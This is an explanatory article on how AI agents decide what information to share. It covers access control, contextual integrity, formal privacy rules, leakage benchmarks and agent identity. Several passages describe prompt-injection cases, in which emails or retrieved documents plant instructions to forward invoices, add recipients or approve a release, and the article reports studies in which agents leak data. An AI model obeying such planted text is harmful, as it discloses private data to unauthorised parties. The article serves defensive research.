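# Context-dependent information control for AI agents: judging, transforming and tracking what they share

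## Why permission to read data is not permission to share it

Context-dependent information control is a family of methods for governing what an AI agent shares, with whom and in what form. An agent here is a language model that pursues a task for a user by calling tools, reading data and taking actions. For example, it may search a mailbox, query a customer database, draft a summary and email the result. Most older security controls determine who may open which file or table, while context-dependent controls determine whether a particular piece of information should pass from a sender to a recipient (an "information flow"), given who the parties are, what the information is for and what the people involved expect. The methods draw on computer security, database research and the philosophy of privacy, and they can allow a request, refuse it or return an altered version of the data.

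*An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Baek, Noh and colleagues, 2026) describes a joint exercise of the Korean and Singaporean AI safety institutes in which an agent worked as a personal assistant at an invented company. The agent had to schedule a second meeting with an outside firm, email a recap of the previous meeting to everyone who had attended, including the firm, and remind its own colleagues about an item in the notes on whether to sue the firm for breach of contract. The agent can't send the reminder without access to the whole file, but once it has that access, the file's permissions can't keep the possible lawsuit out of the recap.

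### How an agent handles data

An agent works in a loop. The model starts from a prompt, which contains its standing instructions and the user's request. It then writes a tool call, a structured line that names a tool and gives its inputs, such as a search term for the mailbox or an address and body for an email. Ordinary software runs the call and adds the result to the text in front of the model, and the model writes its next step. A search over a company's files likewise adds the passages that match best to this text. Many agents also keep a memory, which consists of notes saved in one session and read in another, and some send parts of the job to other agents by message. Halfway through a task, the model's working text may contain a customer's address, a colleague's complaint and a password from a log file, and any later step can use any of it.

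An operator could control what a chatbot shared by filtering its answers before they reached the user. Lahjouji and Colaco argue in their survey *Agents That Know Too Much* (2026) that agents remove this single checkpoint, because sensitive data can also leave in a database query, in the values passed to a tool, in a memory entry or in a message to another agent. For example, an agent that emails a recap does so through a tool call. If the recap contains sensitive data, that data has already been disclosed by the time the agent tells its user that the email was sent, and a filter on that final message would find nothing to block.

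Checking only the final answer can miss leaks elsewhere in the system. *AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) covers 1,000 scenarios in healthcare, finance, law and corporate work, and distinguishes seven channels: final answers, messages between agents, tool inputs, tool outputs, shared memory, logs and saved files. In one audited workflow, a scheduling agent returned an appointment confirmation that leaked nothing, but its message to a second agent contained the patient's complete medical record. The study measured three of the channels at scale, over 4,979 runs. When several agents shared the work, final answers leaked in 27.2% of runs, messages between agents in 68.8%, and at least one of the three channels in 68.9%. In 41.7% of these multi-agent runs, therefore, the final answer leaked nothing but another channel did. A single agent's final answers leaked in 43.2% of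 runs, so judging by final answers alone would make dividing the work look safer.

These figures rest on a broad definition of leakage. The median scenario held 29 sensitive fields and allowed agents to share three. Any other field in a message between two agents of the same system counted as a violation, even if no outsider saw it. Half the scenarios also included an attacker, and the models date from 2024. The rates are better evidence of what a check on answers alone misses than of how likely harm is.

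Baek and colleagues tested three models on twelve routine tasks with no attacker involved. Another model judged the whole record of each run, including the contents of outgoing emails. Between 15% and 58% of runs were both fully correct and fully safe, depending on the model, the set of tasks and the institute running the test. Agents often completed the task but mishandled data while doing it.

### Who may read: roles, attributes and purposes

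Access control determines whether a requester may reach a resource. Its most familiar form, role-based access control, gives each person the permissions attached to their roles, so nurses can open patient charts and payroll clerks can open salary tables. An agent working for a payroll clerk can open the salary table too, but the role's permissions don't specify whom the agent may tell about the salaries.

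Attribute-based access control is finer-grained. The US standards agency's reference, *Guide to Attribute Based Access Control (ABAC) Definition and Considerations* (Hu, Ferraiolo and colleagues, 2014), defines it as authorising requests by evaluating attributes of the requester, the object, the operation and sometimes the surrounding conditions against a policy. A rule might let staff of one office open contracts marked "internal" during working hours. In principle, an administrator could write rules about sending as well as reading. But such a rule relies on the contract's attributes. An agent's three-sentence summary of the contract is a new piece of text, and it has no attributes unless some other mechanism assigns them.

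Purpose-based access control grants access only when the reason for a request matches the purpose for which the organisation collected the data. *Hippocratic Databases* (Agrawal, Kiernan and colleagues, 2002) was an early proposal to build this into the database itself. Each record lists the purposes to which the person has consented, and every query must declare its purpose. In the paper's example, one customer of an online bookseller consents only to the use of her data for the purchase. A second customer also accepts book recommendations but refuses to appear in regional bestseller lists. A query tagged "recommendations" therefore returns only the second customer's books. Further tables list, for each purpose and field, which applications may read the data, which outside parties may receive it and how long the seller may keep it. For example, the delivery company receives the name and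 shipping address, while the card company receives the name and card details.

This comes close to what agents need, since it names recipients as well as readers. But Agrawal and colleagues were frank about its limits. They imagine a dishonest employee in customer service who cannot get at card numbers and asks instead for the email addresses of all registered customers. Both access checks let the query through, because customer service reads email addresses every day. Only a separate component, which compares each query with past habits, flags it. They also found that their design limits disclosure well when the set of recipients is clear at the moment the customer hands over the data, and they left open the case in which recipients emerge later. For an agent, recipients emerge all the time: they are whoever happens to be on the email thread. And the database governs the query. What an agent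 writes once the rows have come back is outside its reach. (A declared purpose may also be false, which is a problem of its own.)

Zhou and Zhang (2026), in *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*, describe an assistant that prepares a report from approved records. It may open the records, send them to an outside analysis service, pass the draft to a second agent for review, and deliver the result to someone outside the organisation. They state that each step needs its own authorisation, and that valid permission for one step does not carry over to the next.

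Without safeguards, agents tend to treat permission to read data as permission to share it. *ArguShield* (Fu and Fu, 2026) tested four models on 120 invented tasks in travel, shopping and healthcare, giving them a user profile full of personal details. An unprotected agent asked to book a hotel may copy the guest's passport number and home address from the profile into the booking form because the form has room for them. The unprotected agents completed 96% of tasks, but measuring completion alone would have missed these disclosures. Their rate of unauthorised silent release, meaning disclosure of values that required the user's approval or should have been withheld, was 0.81 on ordinary tasks and 0.77 on high-risk ones.

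One option is to let the agent read less. That may be enough for the passport number, but it does not help with the meeting notes, because the agent needs the sensitive item to send it to the right people.

### Context, labels and planted instructions

The most influential account of what access rules leave out is contextual integrity, philosopher Helen Nissenbaum's theory that privacy means information flows according to the norms of its social context. Privacy in this sense doesn't require secrecy, since a patient's diagnosis should reach the specialist, though not the employer. Assessing a flow requires specifying five parameters: the data subject (whom the information is about), the sender, the recipient, the type of information, and the transmission principle, which is the condition under which the flow is allowed, such as consent, confidentiality or legal duty. For example, a US resident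 sends income details to the tax authority on condition that they stay confidential. If the authority then passes the same return to a newspaper, the subject and the information are unchanged, but the recipient is new and the condition is broken.

An access rule typically specifies only who may read which resource. Another scenario from Baek and colleagues shows why that is not enough. An agent must post requests about the same important customer to two partner firms. The firm that registers the contract may learn the plan and the payment status but not the customer's name or address. The delivery firm may learn the name, the address and a partly masked phone number but not the plan or the payment status. A single ranking of the fields from harmless to secret cannot express these rules, because each firm may see fields that the other may not. The rule has to include the recipient, and putting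 such norms into a form that software can apply is a large task.

In security, a label is a mark on data that records who may read it (confidentiality) or how far to trust its source (integrity). Labels could solve the problem of the summary that has no attributes, if software can carry the labels over to the new text when a model rewrites the original.

Prompt injection is text that someone puts in data an agent reads so that the agent will follow it as an instruction. A stranger might email the agent an instruction to forward the latest invoices to a new address. If the agent may read invoices and may send mail, forwarding them breaks neither permission. Zhou and Zhang distinguish context that informs a decision about sharing from permission to share. A trusted company directory can supply the address of a recipient whom the user has already approved. If a retrieved document contains an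 instruction to copy in somebody else, that instruction only proposes a new recipient. The document has no authority to approve one, however relevant its contents are to the task.

### One quarterly report, two versions

*A Vision for Access Control in LLM-based Agent Systems* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2025) proposes replacing yes-or-no access decisions with Agent Access Control, a scheme with two modules. The contextual evaluation module considers who is asking, their relationship to the agent, whether the setting is a business meeting or a private conversation, whether they seem to want a summary or to extract the raw data, and which legal, ethical and cultural norms apply. The adaptive response module then adjusts what the agent shares. It can reduce the level of detail, mask names and identifying numbers, or paraphrase, for instance by turning proprietary technical details into general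 insights for a collaborator.

Their worked example is a sensitive quarterly financial report. A senior manager asks the agent to summarise it for the board meeting. The evaluation confirms her high clearance and the formal business setting, so she gets a detailed summary with specific figures and client information. When a junior analyst makes the same request, the evaluation finds that his intention is legitimate but that his role doesn't require all the sensitive data. A binary rule would have either refused him or given him everything. Instead, he gets a high-level overview that omits the sensitive figures, masks client names and rewords proprietary strategies as general remarks about "exploring new markets".

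This example makes a better case for the second module than for the first. The two requests have the same wording and stated occasion, and neither person means any harm, so they differ only in the rank of the person asking. A company could get much the same result from role-based access control and two versions of the report on file. A harder test would keep the person the same and change the situation, for example by having the manager ask for the same summary for an email to a supplier. The example also ignores the recipient. Both summaries are for the board meeting, so the board members will end up with the information. If the analyst is preparing the board's papers, the less detailed summary may well be the wrong one.

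Li and colleagues call for a reasoning engine that judges what an agent may share and operates independently of the agent's main model. Attackers can manipulate the main model through the text it reads from strangers, so it should not be responsible for its own security. The engine would receive the context but take no part in the task, and would focus on risk and permission. They envision a small hybrid system in which a neural component interprets the social situation and a symbolic component applies formal rules, such as giving each party only the access it needs, so that decisions are deterministic and explainable.

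Elsewhere, though, the same paper describes access control as an intrinsic capability of the agent and rejects the idea of an external gate. It lists training the engine into the model, or giving it dedicated neurons, as ways to build it, and argues that only such deep integration can be fast and faithful enough for real-time use. The two designs have different weaknesses. A separate engine adds delay and may lack context that the main model has. A built-in engine is exposed to whatever a planted instruction does to the model around it, which was the original reason for separating them. A separate engine is also vulnerable if it reads the same poisoned document.

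The paper does not settle the matter, because it is a position paper with no implementation or tests. Li and colleagues contribute a clear statement of the goal, but they acknowledge that suitable policy languages and benchmarks are still missing. Experiments are needed to find out whether any model can judge context well enough to reach that goal.

### From a request to an outcome

An agent that is about to pass something on has four possible outcomes open to it. It can release the information as it stands, transform it, withhold it, or ask a person. Fu and Fu's system sorts each value in an outgoing tool call into keep, ask or hide; transformation is what Li and colleagues add. Asking counts as withholding until the person replies. Getting to one of the four takes a chain of decisions:

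1. Establish who is making the request, on whose behalf and for what purpose.
2. Decide which data the agent may read for that purpose.
3. Identify the actual recipient of each message, tool call or memory entry, who may not be the person asking.
4. Judge whether the norms of the context let this information reach that recipient, and on what condition.
5. If they allow only part of it, find a form that still serves the task and check that the forbidden part is really gone.
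6. Make sure that someone with the authority to release restricted data has approved the release, by a standing rule or on the spot.
7. Keep a record of what has gone out, since several harmless disclosures can add up to a harmful one.

An agent sharing the meeting notes can reach all four outcomes within a few minutes. It releases the reminder about the lawsuit to its colleagues, sends the outside firm a recap of only the agreed points, and withholds any mention of the lawsuit from that firm. If an unfamiliar address then appears on the internal thread, the agent should ask.

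Relying on an agent to ask its user before sharing confidential information is less safe than it looks. The security company Cyberhaven had agents prepare and publish a product report from files that included confidential board papers, in a test that Business Quarter described in *AI agents disclose confidential corporate information* (2026). Confidential information became public in 87 of 100 runs. In 69 of those 87 the agent had not raised the relevant material with the simulated user, and in 54 it published before the user had replied. Cyberhaven sells data-security software and simulated a single company, so the rate may not apply elsewhere. The underlying problem probably does, because if the agent alone decides when a case is doubtful enough to ask about, the user may never be asked.

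## Stating norms for information flows as rules

An agent can't judge whether a flow fits the norms of its context until someone has worked out what those norms are. Contextual integrity offers a procedure for that, although Nissenbaum (2004) developed it in *Privacy as Contextual Integrity* to address public surveillance through shopper cards, closed-circuit television and other ways of collecting facts that people have already exposed to somebody. The leading theories of privacy dealt badly with such cases, where it is hard to say what secret anyone has lost. Nissenbaum argued that information should follow the norms of its context. She built on the work of the political philosopher Michael Walzer, who held that different spheres of life distribute their goods by different principles. For example, a fair way to sell cars may be an unfair way to allocate medical care.

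### Contexts and the five parameters

A context in this theory is a social domain, such as healthcare, education or family life. Nissenbaum (2019), in *Contextual Integrity Up and Down the Data Food Chain*, describes a context as a set of roles (physician, patient), activities (examinations, blood tests), kinds of information (symptoms, diagnoses) and norms, all oriented towards certain purposes and values. She concedes that her earlier work gave the purposes too little emphasis, and now holds that they define a context. People also argue about the purposes more than the other parts of a context. They agree that healthcare exists to cure and prevent disease, for example, but disagree about which matters more.

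"Context" is often read more loosely. In 2012 the White House proposed a Consumer Privacy Bill of Rights, under which companies would use data in ways consistent with the context in which consumers had provided it. Nissenbaum (2015), in *Respecting Context to Protect Privacy*, suspected that companies and privacy campaigners could both welcome this principle because they understood it differently. "Context" could mean a technical platform, an industry sector, a business model or a social domain. On the business-model reading, a firm whose business is selling customer profiles respects context when it sells them. On the platform reading, all email is one context, although different norms apply to messages to a doctor, a landlord and a sister in the same mailbox. An agent could easily make this mistake, because software can easily detect that it is handling email.

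The five parameters (subject, sender, recipient, information type and transmission principle) make it possible to compare an old practice with a new one. Nissenbaum argues that a shop changes the transmission principle when it installs a camera, because customers can no longer see who is watching them. This is her reply to the defence that passers-by could always see the customers. When the political consultancy Cambridge Analytica obtained Facebook users' data, people objected to the recipient as well as to the missing consent.

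Leaving out a parameter makes a flow impossible to judge. For example, the statement "the employer's agent sent Dana's salary to the bank" omits the transmission principle. It could describe Dana asking her employer to confirm her income for a mortgage application, which nobody would object to, or the bank buying the figure to target its advertising, which most people would object to. Nissenbaum cites two large surveys she ran with Kirsten Martin, a business-ethics scholar. They found that people are sensitive to all five parameters and may interpret an incomplete description in different ways. A language model given an incomplete description also has to guess what is missing.

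Transmission principles also include notice, reciprocity and sale. When the principle is consent, a parent or guardian may have to give it on the subject's behalf. An attacker can fake the transmission principle with an email that falsely claims the user's approval. This is one reason *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian, 2026) classifies prompt injection as a violation of contextual norms.

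Nissenbaum allows shortcuts in narrow settings. In a hospital system, the subject is nearly always a patient and there are few possible recipients, so a designer can fix some values in advance. This could help an agent that only books appointments for one clinic, but not a general assistant with access to someone's whole digital life.

### Testing the norm itself

*Privacy in Context / Interactive Glossary*, by Nissenbaum and Shvartzshnaider, sets out the theory's current procedure. The analyst first identifies the context, describes the flow, finds the applicable norms and compares the flow with them. If the flow conforms, the analysis ends. If it breaches a norm, or if no norm covers it (a "lacuna"), the analyst must evaluate the practice, which is the second half of the theory.

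That evaluation has three layers. The analyst considers who gains and who loses, then ethical and political values such as fairness and autonomy, and finally the purposes of the context. Nissenbaum illustrates the last layer with medical confidentiality. Employers want to hire healthy candidates, marketers want to find buyers for a drug, and patients want to keep their diagnoses from both. Weighing these interests against each other might never settle the question. But patients who fear disclosure may lie to their doctors or stay away, which endangers their own health and other people's, and so defeats the purpose of healthcare. The same reasoning supports reporting an infectious disease to public-health officials, even against the patient's wishes.

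In her book *Privacy in Context* (2010), Nissenbaum favored established norms by default, arguing that they usually represent a settled compromise among many interests. She has since acknowledged the objection that a norm may be established because it suits the powerful, and she hopes that the evaluation will expose such cases. The glossary's procedure makes this less likely because it does not evaluate flows that conform to a norm, even an unjust one. She has also dropped the requirement to compare each new practice with an older one, since many digital practices have no suitable predecessor.

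The people who decide on a practice should carry out this evaluation, for example when deciding whether a clinic's agent may send visit summaries to an employer's wellness scheme at all. An agent deciding whether to send one email cannot do so, and needs the result in a form that software can apply.

### From a norm to a formula

*Privacy and Contextual Integrity* (Barth, Datta and colleagues, 2006), which Nissenbaum co-wrote, expresses part of the theory in formal logic. In its model, people act in roles and send messages that contain attributes of some person, such as a diagnosis. A positive norm allows a flow if its condition holds, and a negative norm forbids a flow unless its condition holds. A message is acceptable if at least one positive norm allows it and no negative norm forbids it.

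The conditions can refer to time. Temporal logic adds operators to ordinary logic, including □ ("at every moment"), ◇ ("now or at some later moment") and a past operator, written ◆ below ("at some earlier moment"). Role-based access control has no equivalent, so a nurse's permission to open a file does not depend on what the patient signed last week.

A rule from HIPAA, the main US law on the privacy of medical records, shows how a translation works. According to the US health department (HHS) guidance *Does the HIPAA Privacy Rule permit a covered entity to disclose psychotherapy notes*, an organisation bound by the law must, with few exceptions, obtain the patient's written authorisation before disclosing psychotherapy notes, even to another health-care provider. The five parameters are easy to fill in: the sender is a hospital, the recipient is a clinician elsewhere, the subject is a patient,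 the information type is psychotherapy notes, and the transmission principle is the patient's prior written authorisation.

This restriction operates against a more general permission, under which a hospital may send health information to a clinician who is treating the patient. With *s* for the sender, *r* for the recipient, *q* for the patient, *m* for the message and *t* for the type of information, the two norms and the rule that combines them are:

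```
Permission:   hospital(s) ∧ clinician(r) ∧ patient(q)
              ∧ treats(r, q) ∧ health-information(t)

Restriction:  hospital(s) ∧ clinician(r) ∧ patient(q)
              ∧ psychotherapy-notes(t)
              → ◆ authorises(q, s, r, t)

Whole rule:   □ ∀ s, r, q, m, t:
              send(s, r, m) ∧ contains(m, q, t)
              → Permission ∧ Restriction
```

In words: whenever anyone sends a message containing information about a patient, the permission must hold, and if the information is psychotherapy notes, the patient must already have authorised that hospital to send them to that recipient. (The formula omits HIPAA's exceptions, such as one for a hospital's own training programmes.)

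Suppose a patient signs an authorisation on Monday naming a psychiatrist at another clinic, who has started treating her. On Wednesday the hospital's agent sends the patient's psychotherapy notes to the psychiatrist. The roles match, the psychiatrist is treating her, and psychotherapy notes are a kind of health information, so the permission holds. The patient signed the authorisation before the agent sent the notes, so the restriction holds too, and the rule allows the message.

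Suppose she signs on Thursday instead. The permission still holds on Wednesday, but no earlier authorisation exists then, so the rule forbids the message. The people and the notes are the same in both cases, so a table listing who may read which file could not distinguish the two cases.

Translation errors are easy to make, and this formula contains one. If the patient signs on Monday and revokes the authorisation on Tuesday, "at some earlier moment she authorised it" remains true on Wednesday and forever after. HIPAA lets patients revoke, so the condition should require that she has authorised the disclosure and has not revoked it since. Temporal logic has an operator S, "since", for exactly this:

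```
¬revokes(q, s, r, t)  S  authorises(q, s, r, t)
```

The formula is also weak because *treats(r, q)* records a relationship, whereas HIPAA's permission depends on a purpose. A psychiatrist treating the patient might want the notes for a research project. Anupam Datta, one of Nissenbaum's co-authors on the logic, has urged her to add a sixth parameter for use, and Nissenbaum writes that she is increasingly persuaded. Her example is a company takeover, in which the buyer acquires data that the seller might not have been allowed to send it.

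Conditions on the future are harder to enforce. The slides *Understanding Privacy and Contextual Integrity* analyse a clause of the Gramm-Leach-Bliley Act, a US law on financial privacy. A bank that shares a customer's private information with an unaffiliated company must notify the customer before or after the sharing, which is written as "◆ notifies or ◇ notifies". Software can look up past notices when the bank sends the data, but if there are none, it can only record the duty to notify and check later. Without a deadline, an auditor can't prove a violation from any log, because the bank might still send the notice later.

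Barth and colleagues showed that their model could express many provisions of HIPAA, Gramm-Leach-Bliley and COPPA (the US law on children's data online). They also showed that standard decision procedures for temporal logic can answer important questions about such rules, including how an organisation's policy relates to a legal standard. Before an agent sends any messages, a hospital could check whether its policy allows something the law forbids.

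The logic only compares flows with norms and does not evaluate the norms themselves. It also takes the basic facts as given, so someone or something else must establish that the recipient is a clinician and that a message contains psychotherapy notes. Suppose an agent learns from the notes that a patient "has been struggling since the divorce" and writes this to a colleague. The formula gives the right answer only if something has correctly classified that sentence as content from the notes.

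### Where the norms come from

Much of the statute law from which an agent's norms could be drawn consists of standards that still need interpreting. HIPAA's minimum-necessary standard requires reasonable efforts to limit a disclosure to what is necessary for its purpose. (It doesn't apply to disclosures to a provider for treatment, so it would not have protected the notes above.) The European Union's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) has two comparable principles, which Lahjouji and Colaco count among the governing principles of data-protection regulation in general. Purpose limitation requires organisations to collect data for specified, explicit and legitimate purposes and not to process it further in ways incompatible with them. Data minimisation requires organisations to limit the data to what is necessary for those purposes. An agent that gives a courier a customer's address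 but not her order history complies with data minimisation. Whether it may use the order history to draft a marketing email depends on whether that purpose is compatible with the original one. The regulation lists factors to consider, including the relationship in which the organisation collected the data, but gives no formula for weighing them.

Some statutory rules are more definite. A HIPAA provision in the eCFR, the US government's online edition of federal regulations, covers organisations that provide healthcare alongside other activities. The healthcare part must generally treat the rest of the organisation as an outsider. A university clinic therefore can't pass a student's record to the housing office just because both belong to the university. So an agent with access to a whole organisation's files needs to know more about a recipient than that they are internal.

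Data minimisation and contextual integrity overlap, but they can conflict. Nissenbaum explicitly rejects the idea that privacy means sharing less. A referral letter that omits the patient's allergies discloses less, but it puts the patient at risk and breaks the norms of medicine.

An organisation's own policy fills some of the gaps in the law. Thornton, Pritom and colleagues (2026), in *Privacy Conductor*, point out that HIPAA may limit who can see a clinical record without specifying which nurse may see which patient's record. In their design, an accountable authority writes that policy, and ordinary software enforces it before the language model receives any document. A role counts only in the context that grants it, so the software refuses a doctor who makes a request in an administrative capacity. The software also requires an assignment, which is a recorded relationship between the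 requester and the person the document is about. They tested the design on an invented clinic in which 24 people each requested all 105 documents. In 602 cases, the document was about a particular person and the requester had a permitted role, but in 367 of these the requester had no assignment to that person. A policy based on roles alone would have released the documents in those 367 cases.

Where neither law nor policy is specific enough, researchers have asked the public. In a factorial vignette survey, they write a template for an information flow, fill its slots with different values and ask people how appropriate each version is. If two versions differ only in the recipient, the difference between their ratings measures how much the recipient matters. With ten possible values for each of the five parameters, there would be 100,000 versions, so researchers simplify the design. In one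 study, Martin and Nissenbaum used a template with only three slots (the type of information, who collects it and how it is used) to keep the questions readable, and acknowledged that a full treatment needs all five parameters.

Shvartzshnaider, Tong and colleagues (2016) turned crowdsourced expectations into rules in Datalog, a logic-programming language, so that software could check flows against them. Any such conversion has to reduce a range of opinions to a yes or a no. If 60% of respondents find a flow acceptable, the rule will misrepresent a large group of them whether it allows or forbids the flow.

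The user's own preferences are the easiest source of rules, since the agent can ask for them. Nissenbaum (2011), in *A Contextual Approach to Privacy Online*, argues against relying on individual choice, because people cannot understand all the relevant facts when they are asked to agree. An agent could improve on a website's privacy notice by asking about one specific disclosure. But much of the information in a mailbox is about other people, and the user can consent only for herself. Her agreement is not enough to disclose a colleague's diagnosis.

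### When norms conflict or run out

Different sources of norms often disagree. *Psychotherapy Notes*, a policy page of the Californian hospital system Loma Linda University Health (LLUH), tells staff that state law protects mental-health records more strongly than HIPAA does. Staff must forward any request for such records to a named department and are not asked to reconcile the two laws. An agent faced with conflicting norms could also forward the request instead of resolving the conflict itself.

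Applying the strictest norm works as long as every norm only limits disclosure, and HIPAA leaves stricter state laws in force. It fails when a norm requires disclosure. US physicians, for example, must report certain diseases even if the patient asks them not to. An agent's operator therefore needs to set an order of precedence in advance. Legal duties and prohibitions must come first. The organisation's policy can then restrict what the law leaves open, and the subject's wishes can restrict it further, except where a duty to disclose applies. The decision procedures of Barth and colleagues can detect a conflict between two sets of rules, but people have to resolve it.

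Flows that no norm covers are harder to handle. Few people have a settled expectation about whether an assistant that transcribed one team's meeting may use the transcript to answer another team's question. The 2006 logic forbids any flow that no positive norm allows, and Thornton and colleagues also make refusal the default. In the theory itself, the lack of a norm is a reason to evaluate the practice, which may show that the flow is beneficial. Refusing by default is sensible for software that can't do this evaluation, but withholding information that the norms call for also breaches them, and Thornton and colleagues count it as a violation just as they do improper sharing. A default refusal does less damage if the agent reports the gap to whoever owns the policy, who can then write a rule.

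Even a good rule goes out of date when privacy norms change. *Contextual Integrity for Computer Systems*, a research project, gives the example of a classroom discussion board that correctly enforces educational privacy norms until massive open online courses change what people expect. The project set out to model such changes formally, but in the meantime people have to review the rules.

### Does language-model research apply the theory?

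Shvartzshnaider and Duddu (2025), in *Position: Contextual Integrity is Inadequately Applied to Language Models*, argue that most researchers who invoke contextual integrity use its terms without applying its substance. They assessed nine works on chatbots and agents against four tenets: that privacy is the appropriate flow of information, that appropriate flows conform to privacy norms, that describing a flow requires all five parameters, and that the norms must be tested ethically.

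| Tenet | Works that satisfied it, of nine |
|---|---|
| Privacy is appropriate flow | 1 |
| Appropriate flows conform to privacy norms | 0 |
| All five parameters describe a flow | 7 |
| An ethical test applies to the norms | 0 |

Researchers had thus adopted the part of the theory that looks most like a data structure. For the first tenet, most of the works measured something else, such as leakage of sensitive data, disclosure beyond what a task needs or violations of a statute. For the second, they treated laws or survey answers as the norms. Shvartzshnaider and Duddu object that the law may allow someone to photograph a stranger on a train even though this could violate the stranger's privacy. Survey answers record individual preferences, which a norm may rightly override, as with disease reporting. They consider surveys a reasonable starting point, but the results then need the ethical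 test, which none of the nine works mentioned. Most of the works also used "context" to mean the setting of a single task, without the roles, values and purposes of a social domain.

Ganesh, More and colleagues (2026), in *Privacy in Context Is Being Overlooked in the Age of General-Purpose LLMs*, endorse this critique and offer evidence that the problem is wider. Of the 31 papers they reviewed on protecting what users type into a language model, more than three quarters proposed a method for all uses rather than for a specific application. All eleven publicly available tools they examined were also for general chatbot use.

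Applying the full framework faithfully would take much more work. Developers would have to identify the social domain and its purposes, and specify the agent's role, since "the user's AI model" is not yet a role with settled duties in medicine or banking. They would also need evidence of actual norms. Kumar (2024) provides a step-by-step method for applying the full framework to interviews, illustrated with data on fitness tracking. Shvartzshnaider and Duddu suggest that agreeing on norms may take deliberation among researchers, government and industry, and that flows that are new or breach existing norms may need a similar process. They think no purely algorithmic method can replace these social processes.

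The main reply is pragmatic. *Reinforcement Learning for Scalable and Trustworthy Intelligent Systems* (2026), a thesis that includes work on training models to follow contextual norms, acknowledges that such norms can be subjective, vary and change, which may make them difficult to encode completely. It argues that even partial adherence can make agents more trustworthy in real tasks. This is plausible, because an agent that considers the recipient and the transmission principle is better placed to decide what to share than one that only searches for card numbers, even if no one has tested whether the underlying norm is just.

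The two positions are closer than they look, because Shvartzshnaider and Duddu accept that parts of the framework are useful for checking legal compliance or gauging preferences, and say that the earlier work is not obsolete. They ask researchers who use the framework this way to claim only that the theory inspired them. The disagreement matters in practice when an operator relies on the stronger claim. For example, a hospital that buys an agent "with contextual integrity" may assume that someone has examined whether its information practices serve patients, when the vendor has only checked the agent's outputs against HIPAA and a survey.

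Ganesh and colleagues recommend deploying models for specific applications wherever possible, with safeguards suited to each application. For an agent confined to one clinic, the purposes are known, the roles are few, and a responsible person can write and defend the rules. A general assistant, however, will keep encountering information flows that nobody has written a rule for.

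## Establishing who is asking and for what purpose

Software can apply the rule on psychotherapy notes only if it can establish that the recipient is a clinician, that she is treating this patient and that the patient has signed an authorisation. Where no rule exists, whoever judges the information flow needs the same kinds of facts. Some of these facts are in records that an outsider can't easily change and others are stated only in an email, but a language model receives both as text.

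### Who is acting, and for whom

Online services recognise a caller by its credential, such as a key or a signed token, but a credential proves little about an agent. *AI Identity* (Otsuka, Toyoda and Leung, 2026) distinguishes the identities of the trained model, the configured agent (its standing instructions and tools) and the running process, as well as the authority delegated by a person or organisation. The technology for identifying the running process is the most mature. An infrastructure service checks the process and issues it a short-lived certificate. The certificate proves that a trusted program is connecting, but not what the program will do next, and it remains valid even if the agent has just read a planted instruction.

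Otsuka and colleagues cite figures showing that 45.6% of organisations run their agents on shared keys, so a database can't distinguish the scheduling agent from the billing agent. Google's Agent2Agent protocol lets agents from different companies find each other through "cards" that describe them. According to *AIP* (2026), a proposal for a competing identity scheme, the identities on these cards are self-declared. Unless something else authenticates the connection, a norm that allows information to flow to an insurer's agent could also allow it to flow to any agent that claims to be one.

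When an agent logs in as its user, the service can't tell which of them is acting. *Identity Management for Agentic AI* (2025) recommends tokens that name both. The IETF standard *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (2020) has one field for the person a request is made for and another for the current actor. If Dana's assistant passes a job to a second agent, the new token can name Dana as the subject, the second agent as the actor and the assistant as a prior actor. But services following the standard must ignore prior actors when deciding on access, so a hospital could not refuse a request on the grounds that a marketing firm's agent had handled it earlier. *Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Prasad, Krishnan and colleagues, 2026), a draft standard, proposes formats in which services could verify the chain of actors, as well as simpler ones that only declare it.

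A verified chain shows only who took part. *Bounded Agents* (2026) points out that recording a delegation does not narrow it. A user may let her assistant read all her mail but want the sub-agent that books a restaurant to see only one thread. Some tokens let each holder add restrictions that later holders can't remove, but the restrictions still have to reach the service that acts on them. Zhou and Zhang describe a user who permits an agent to send one summary to one contact. The policy records this correctly, but the software that issues the credential replaces it with a general permission to send mail. The mail service then accepts the credential as valid and will deliver any message the agent sends, to any recipient.

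Agents that serve several people raise a problem that better credentials don't solve. In *The Agent Access Model*, a proposal from the internet company Cloudflare, Silverlock imagines an agent in a shared workspace that summarises a thread using revenue data only one of two colleagues may see. The other colleague then asks about it. The system knows who both people are and what each may read, but the summary no longer shows whose permission it depends on. Restricting the agent to what both may see would prevent the leak but make the agent much less useful. Silverlock knows of no widely deployed system that solves this end to end.

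### Relationship and purpose

A system can't tell from identity alone how the requester is related to the person the data is about. An organisation can verify a relationship if it keeps a record of it, as the clinic simulated by Thornton and colleagues did with its list of assignments. The check is only as accurate as the list, and a nurse who moved to another ward yesterday may still be on it. Outside the organisation there is usually no list. When someone writes that she is the patient's sister and needs the test results, the agent may be able to verify her email address, but it has only her claim that they are related.

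The purpose of a request is harder to establish than who is asking. Each query to a Hippocratic database carries only a declared purpose, which may be false. An agent could instead infer the purpose from the conversation, but Silverlock warns that an attacker can shape this inference with the same text that manipulates the agent. He proposes a task template that a person writes beforehand. For example, a template might allow a nightly reconciliation job to read three named tables and post to one channel. When the job starts, software limits it to actions that the template permits and that both the person who started it and the agent service are allowed to take.

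This verifies that someone with authority declared the purpose and that the agent's actions stay within it. It can't show why the person wants the result. Templates also suit repeated work better than they suit a general assistant, whose user may ask for something new every hour.

### Evidence and authority

Much of the context an agent relies on will therefore remain unverified or come from sources that are reliable only about some things. Zhou and Zhang argue that a system should check both whether a source is trustworthy and which decisions it may influence. In their example, a directory lists Alice as the approved contact, which settles a choice that the user's permission already covers. A retrieved document contains an instruction to copy in Bob, and following it would enlarge that permission.

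Only the user, or someone to whom the user or organisation has given that power, can decide to add a recipient. This holds even if the document is not malicious and Bob does need the report. Nor does the directory authorise sending him the report by listing him as an employee. The user or organisation can give the power in advance. For example, a user may tell her agent to follow her manager's task list within a fixed set of actions, and the list then authorises only those actions.

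Even when a system restricts an answer to "yes" or "no", the answer must come from an authorised source. The restriction leaves untrusted text no room to add a new instruction, but the answer can still cause harm. Zhou and Zhang give the example of a workflow that asks whether a draft is approved for external release, where a single "yes" sends confidential data out of the organisation. If the system takes that answer from a line in the draft, whoever wrote the draft has approved its release. The system has to check that the answer came from the designated approver or from a procedure that the organisation has authorised to decide.

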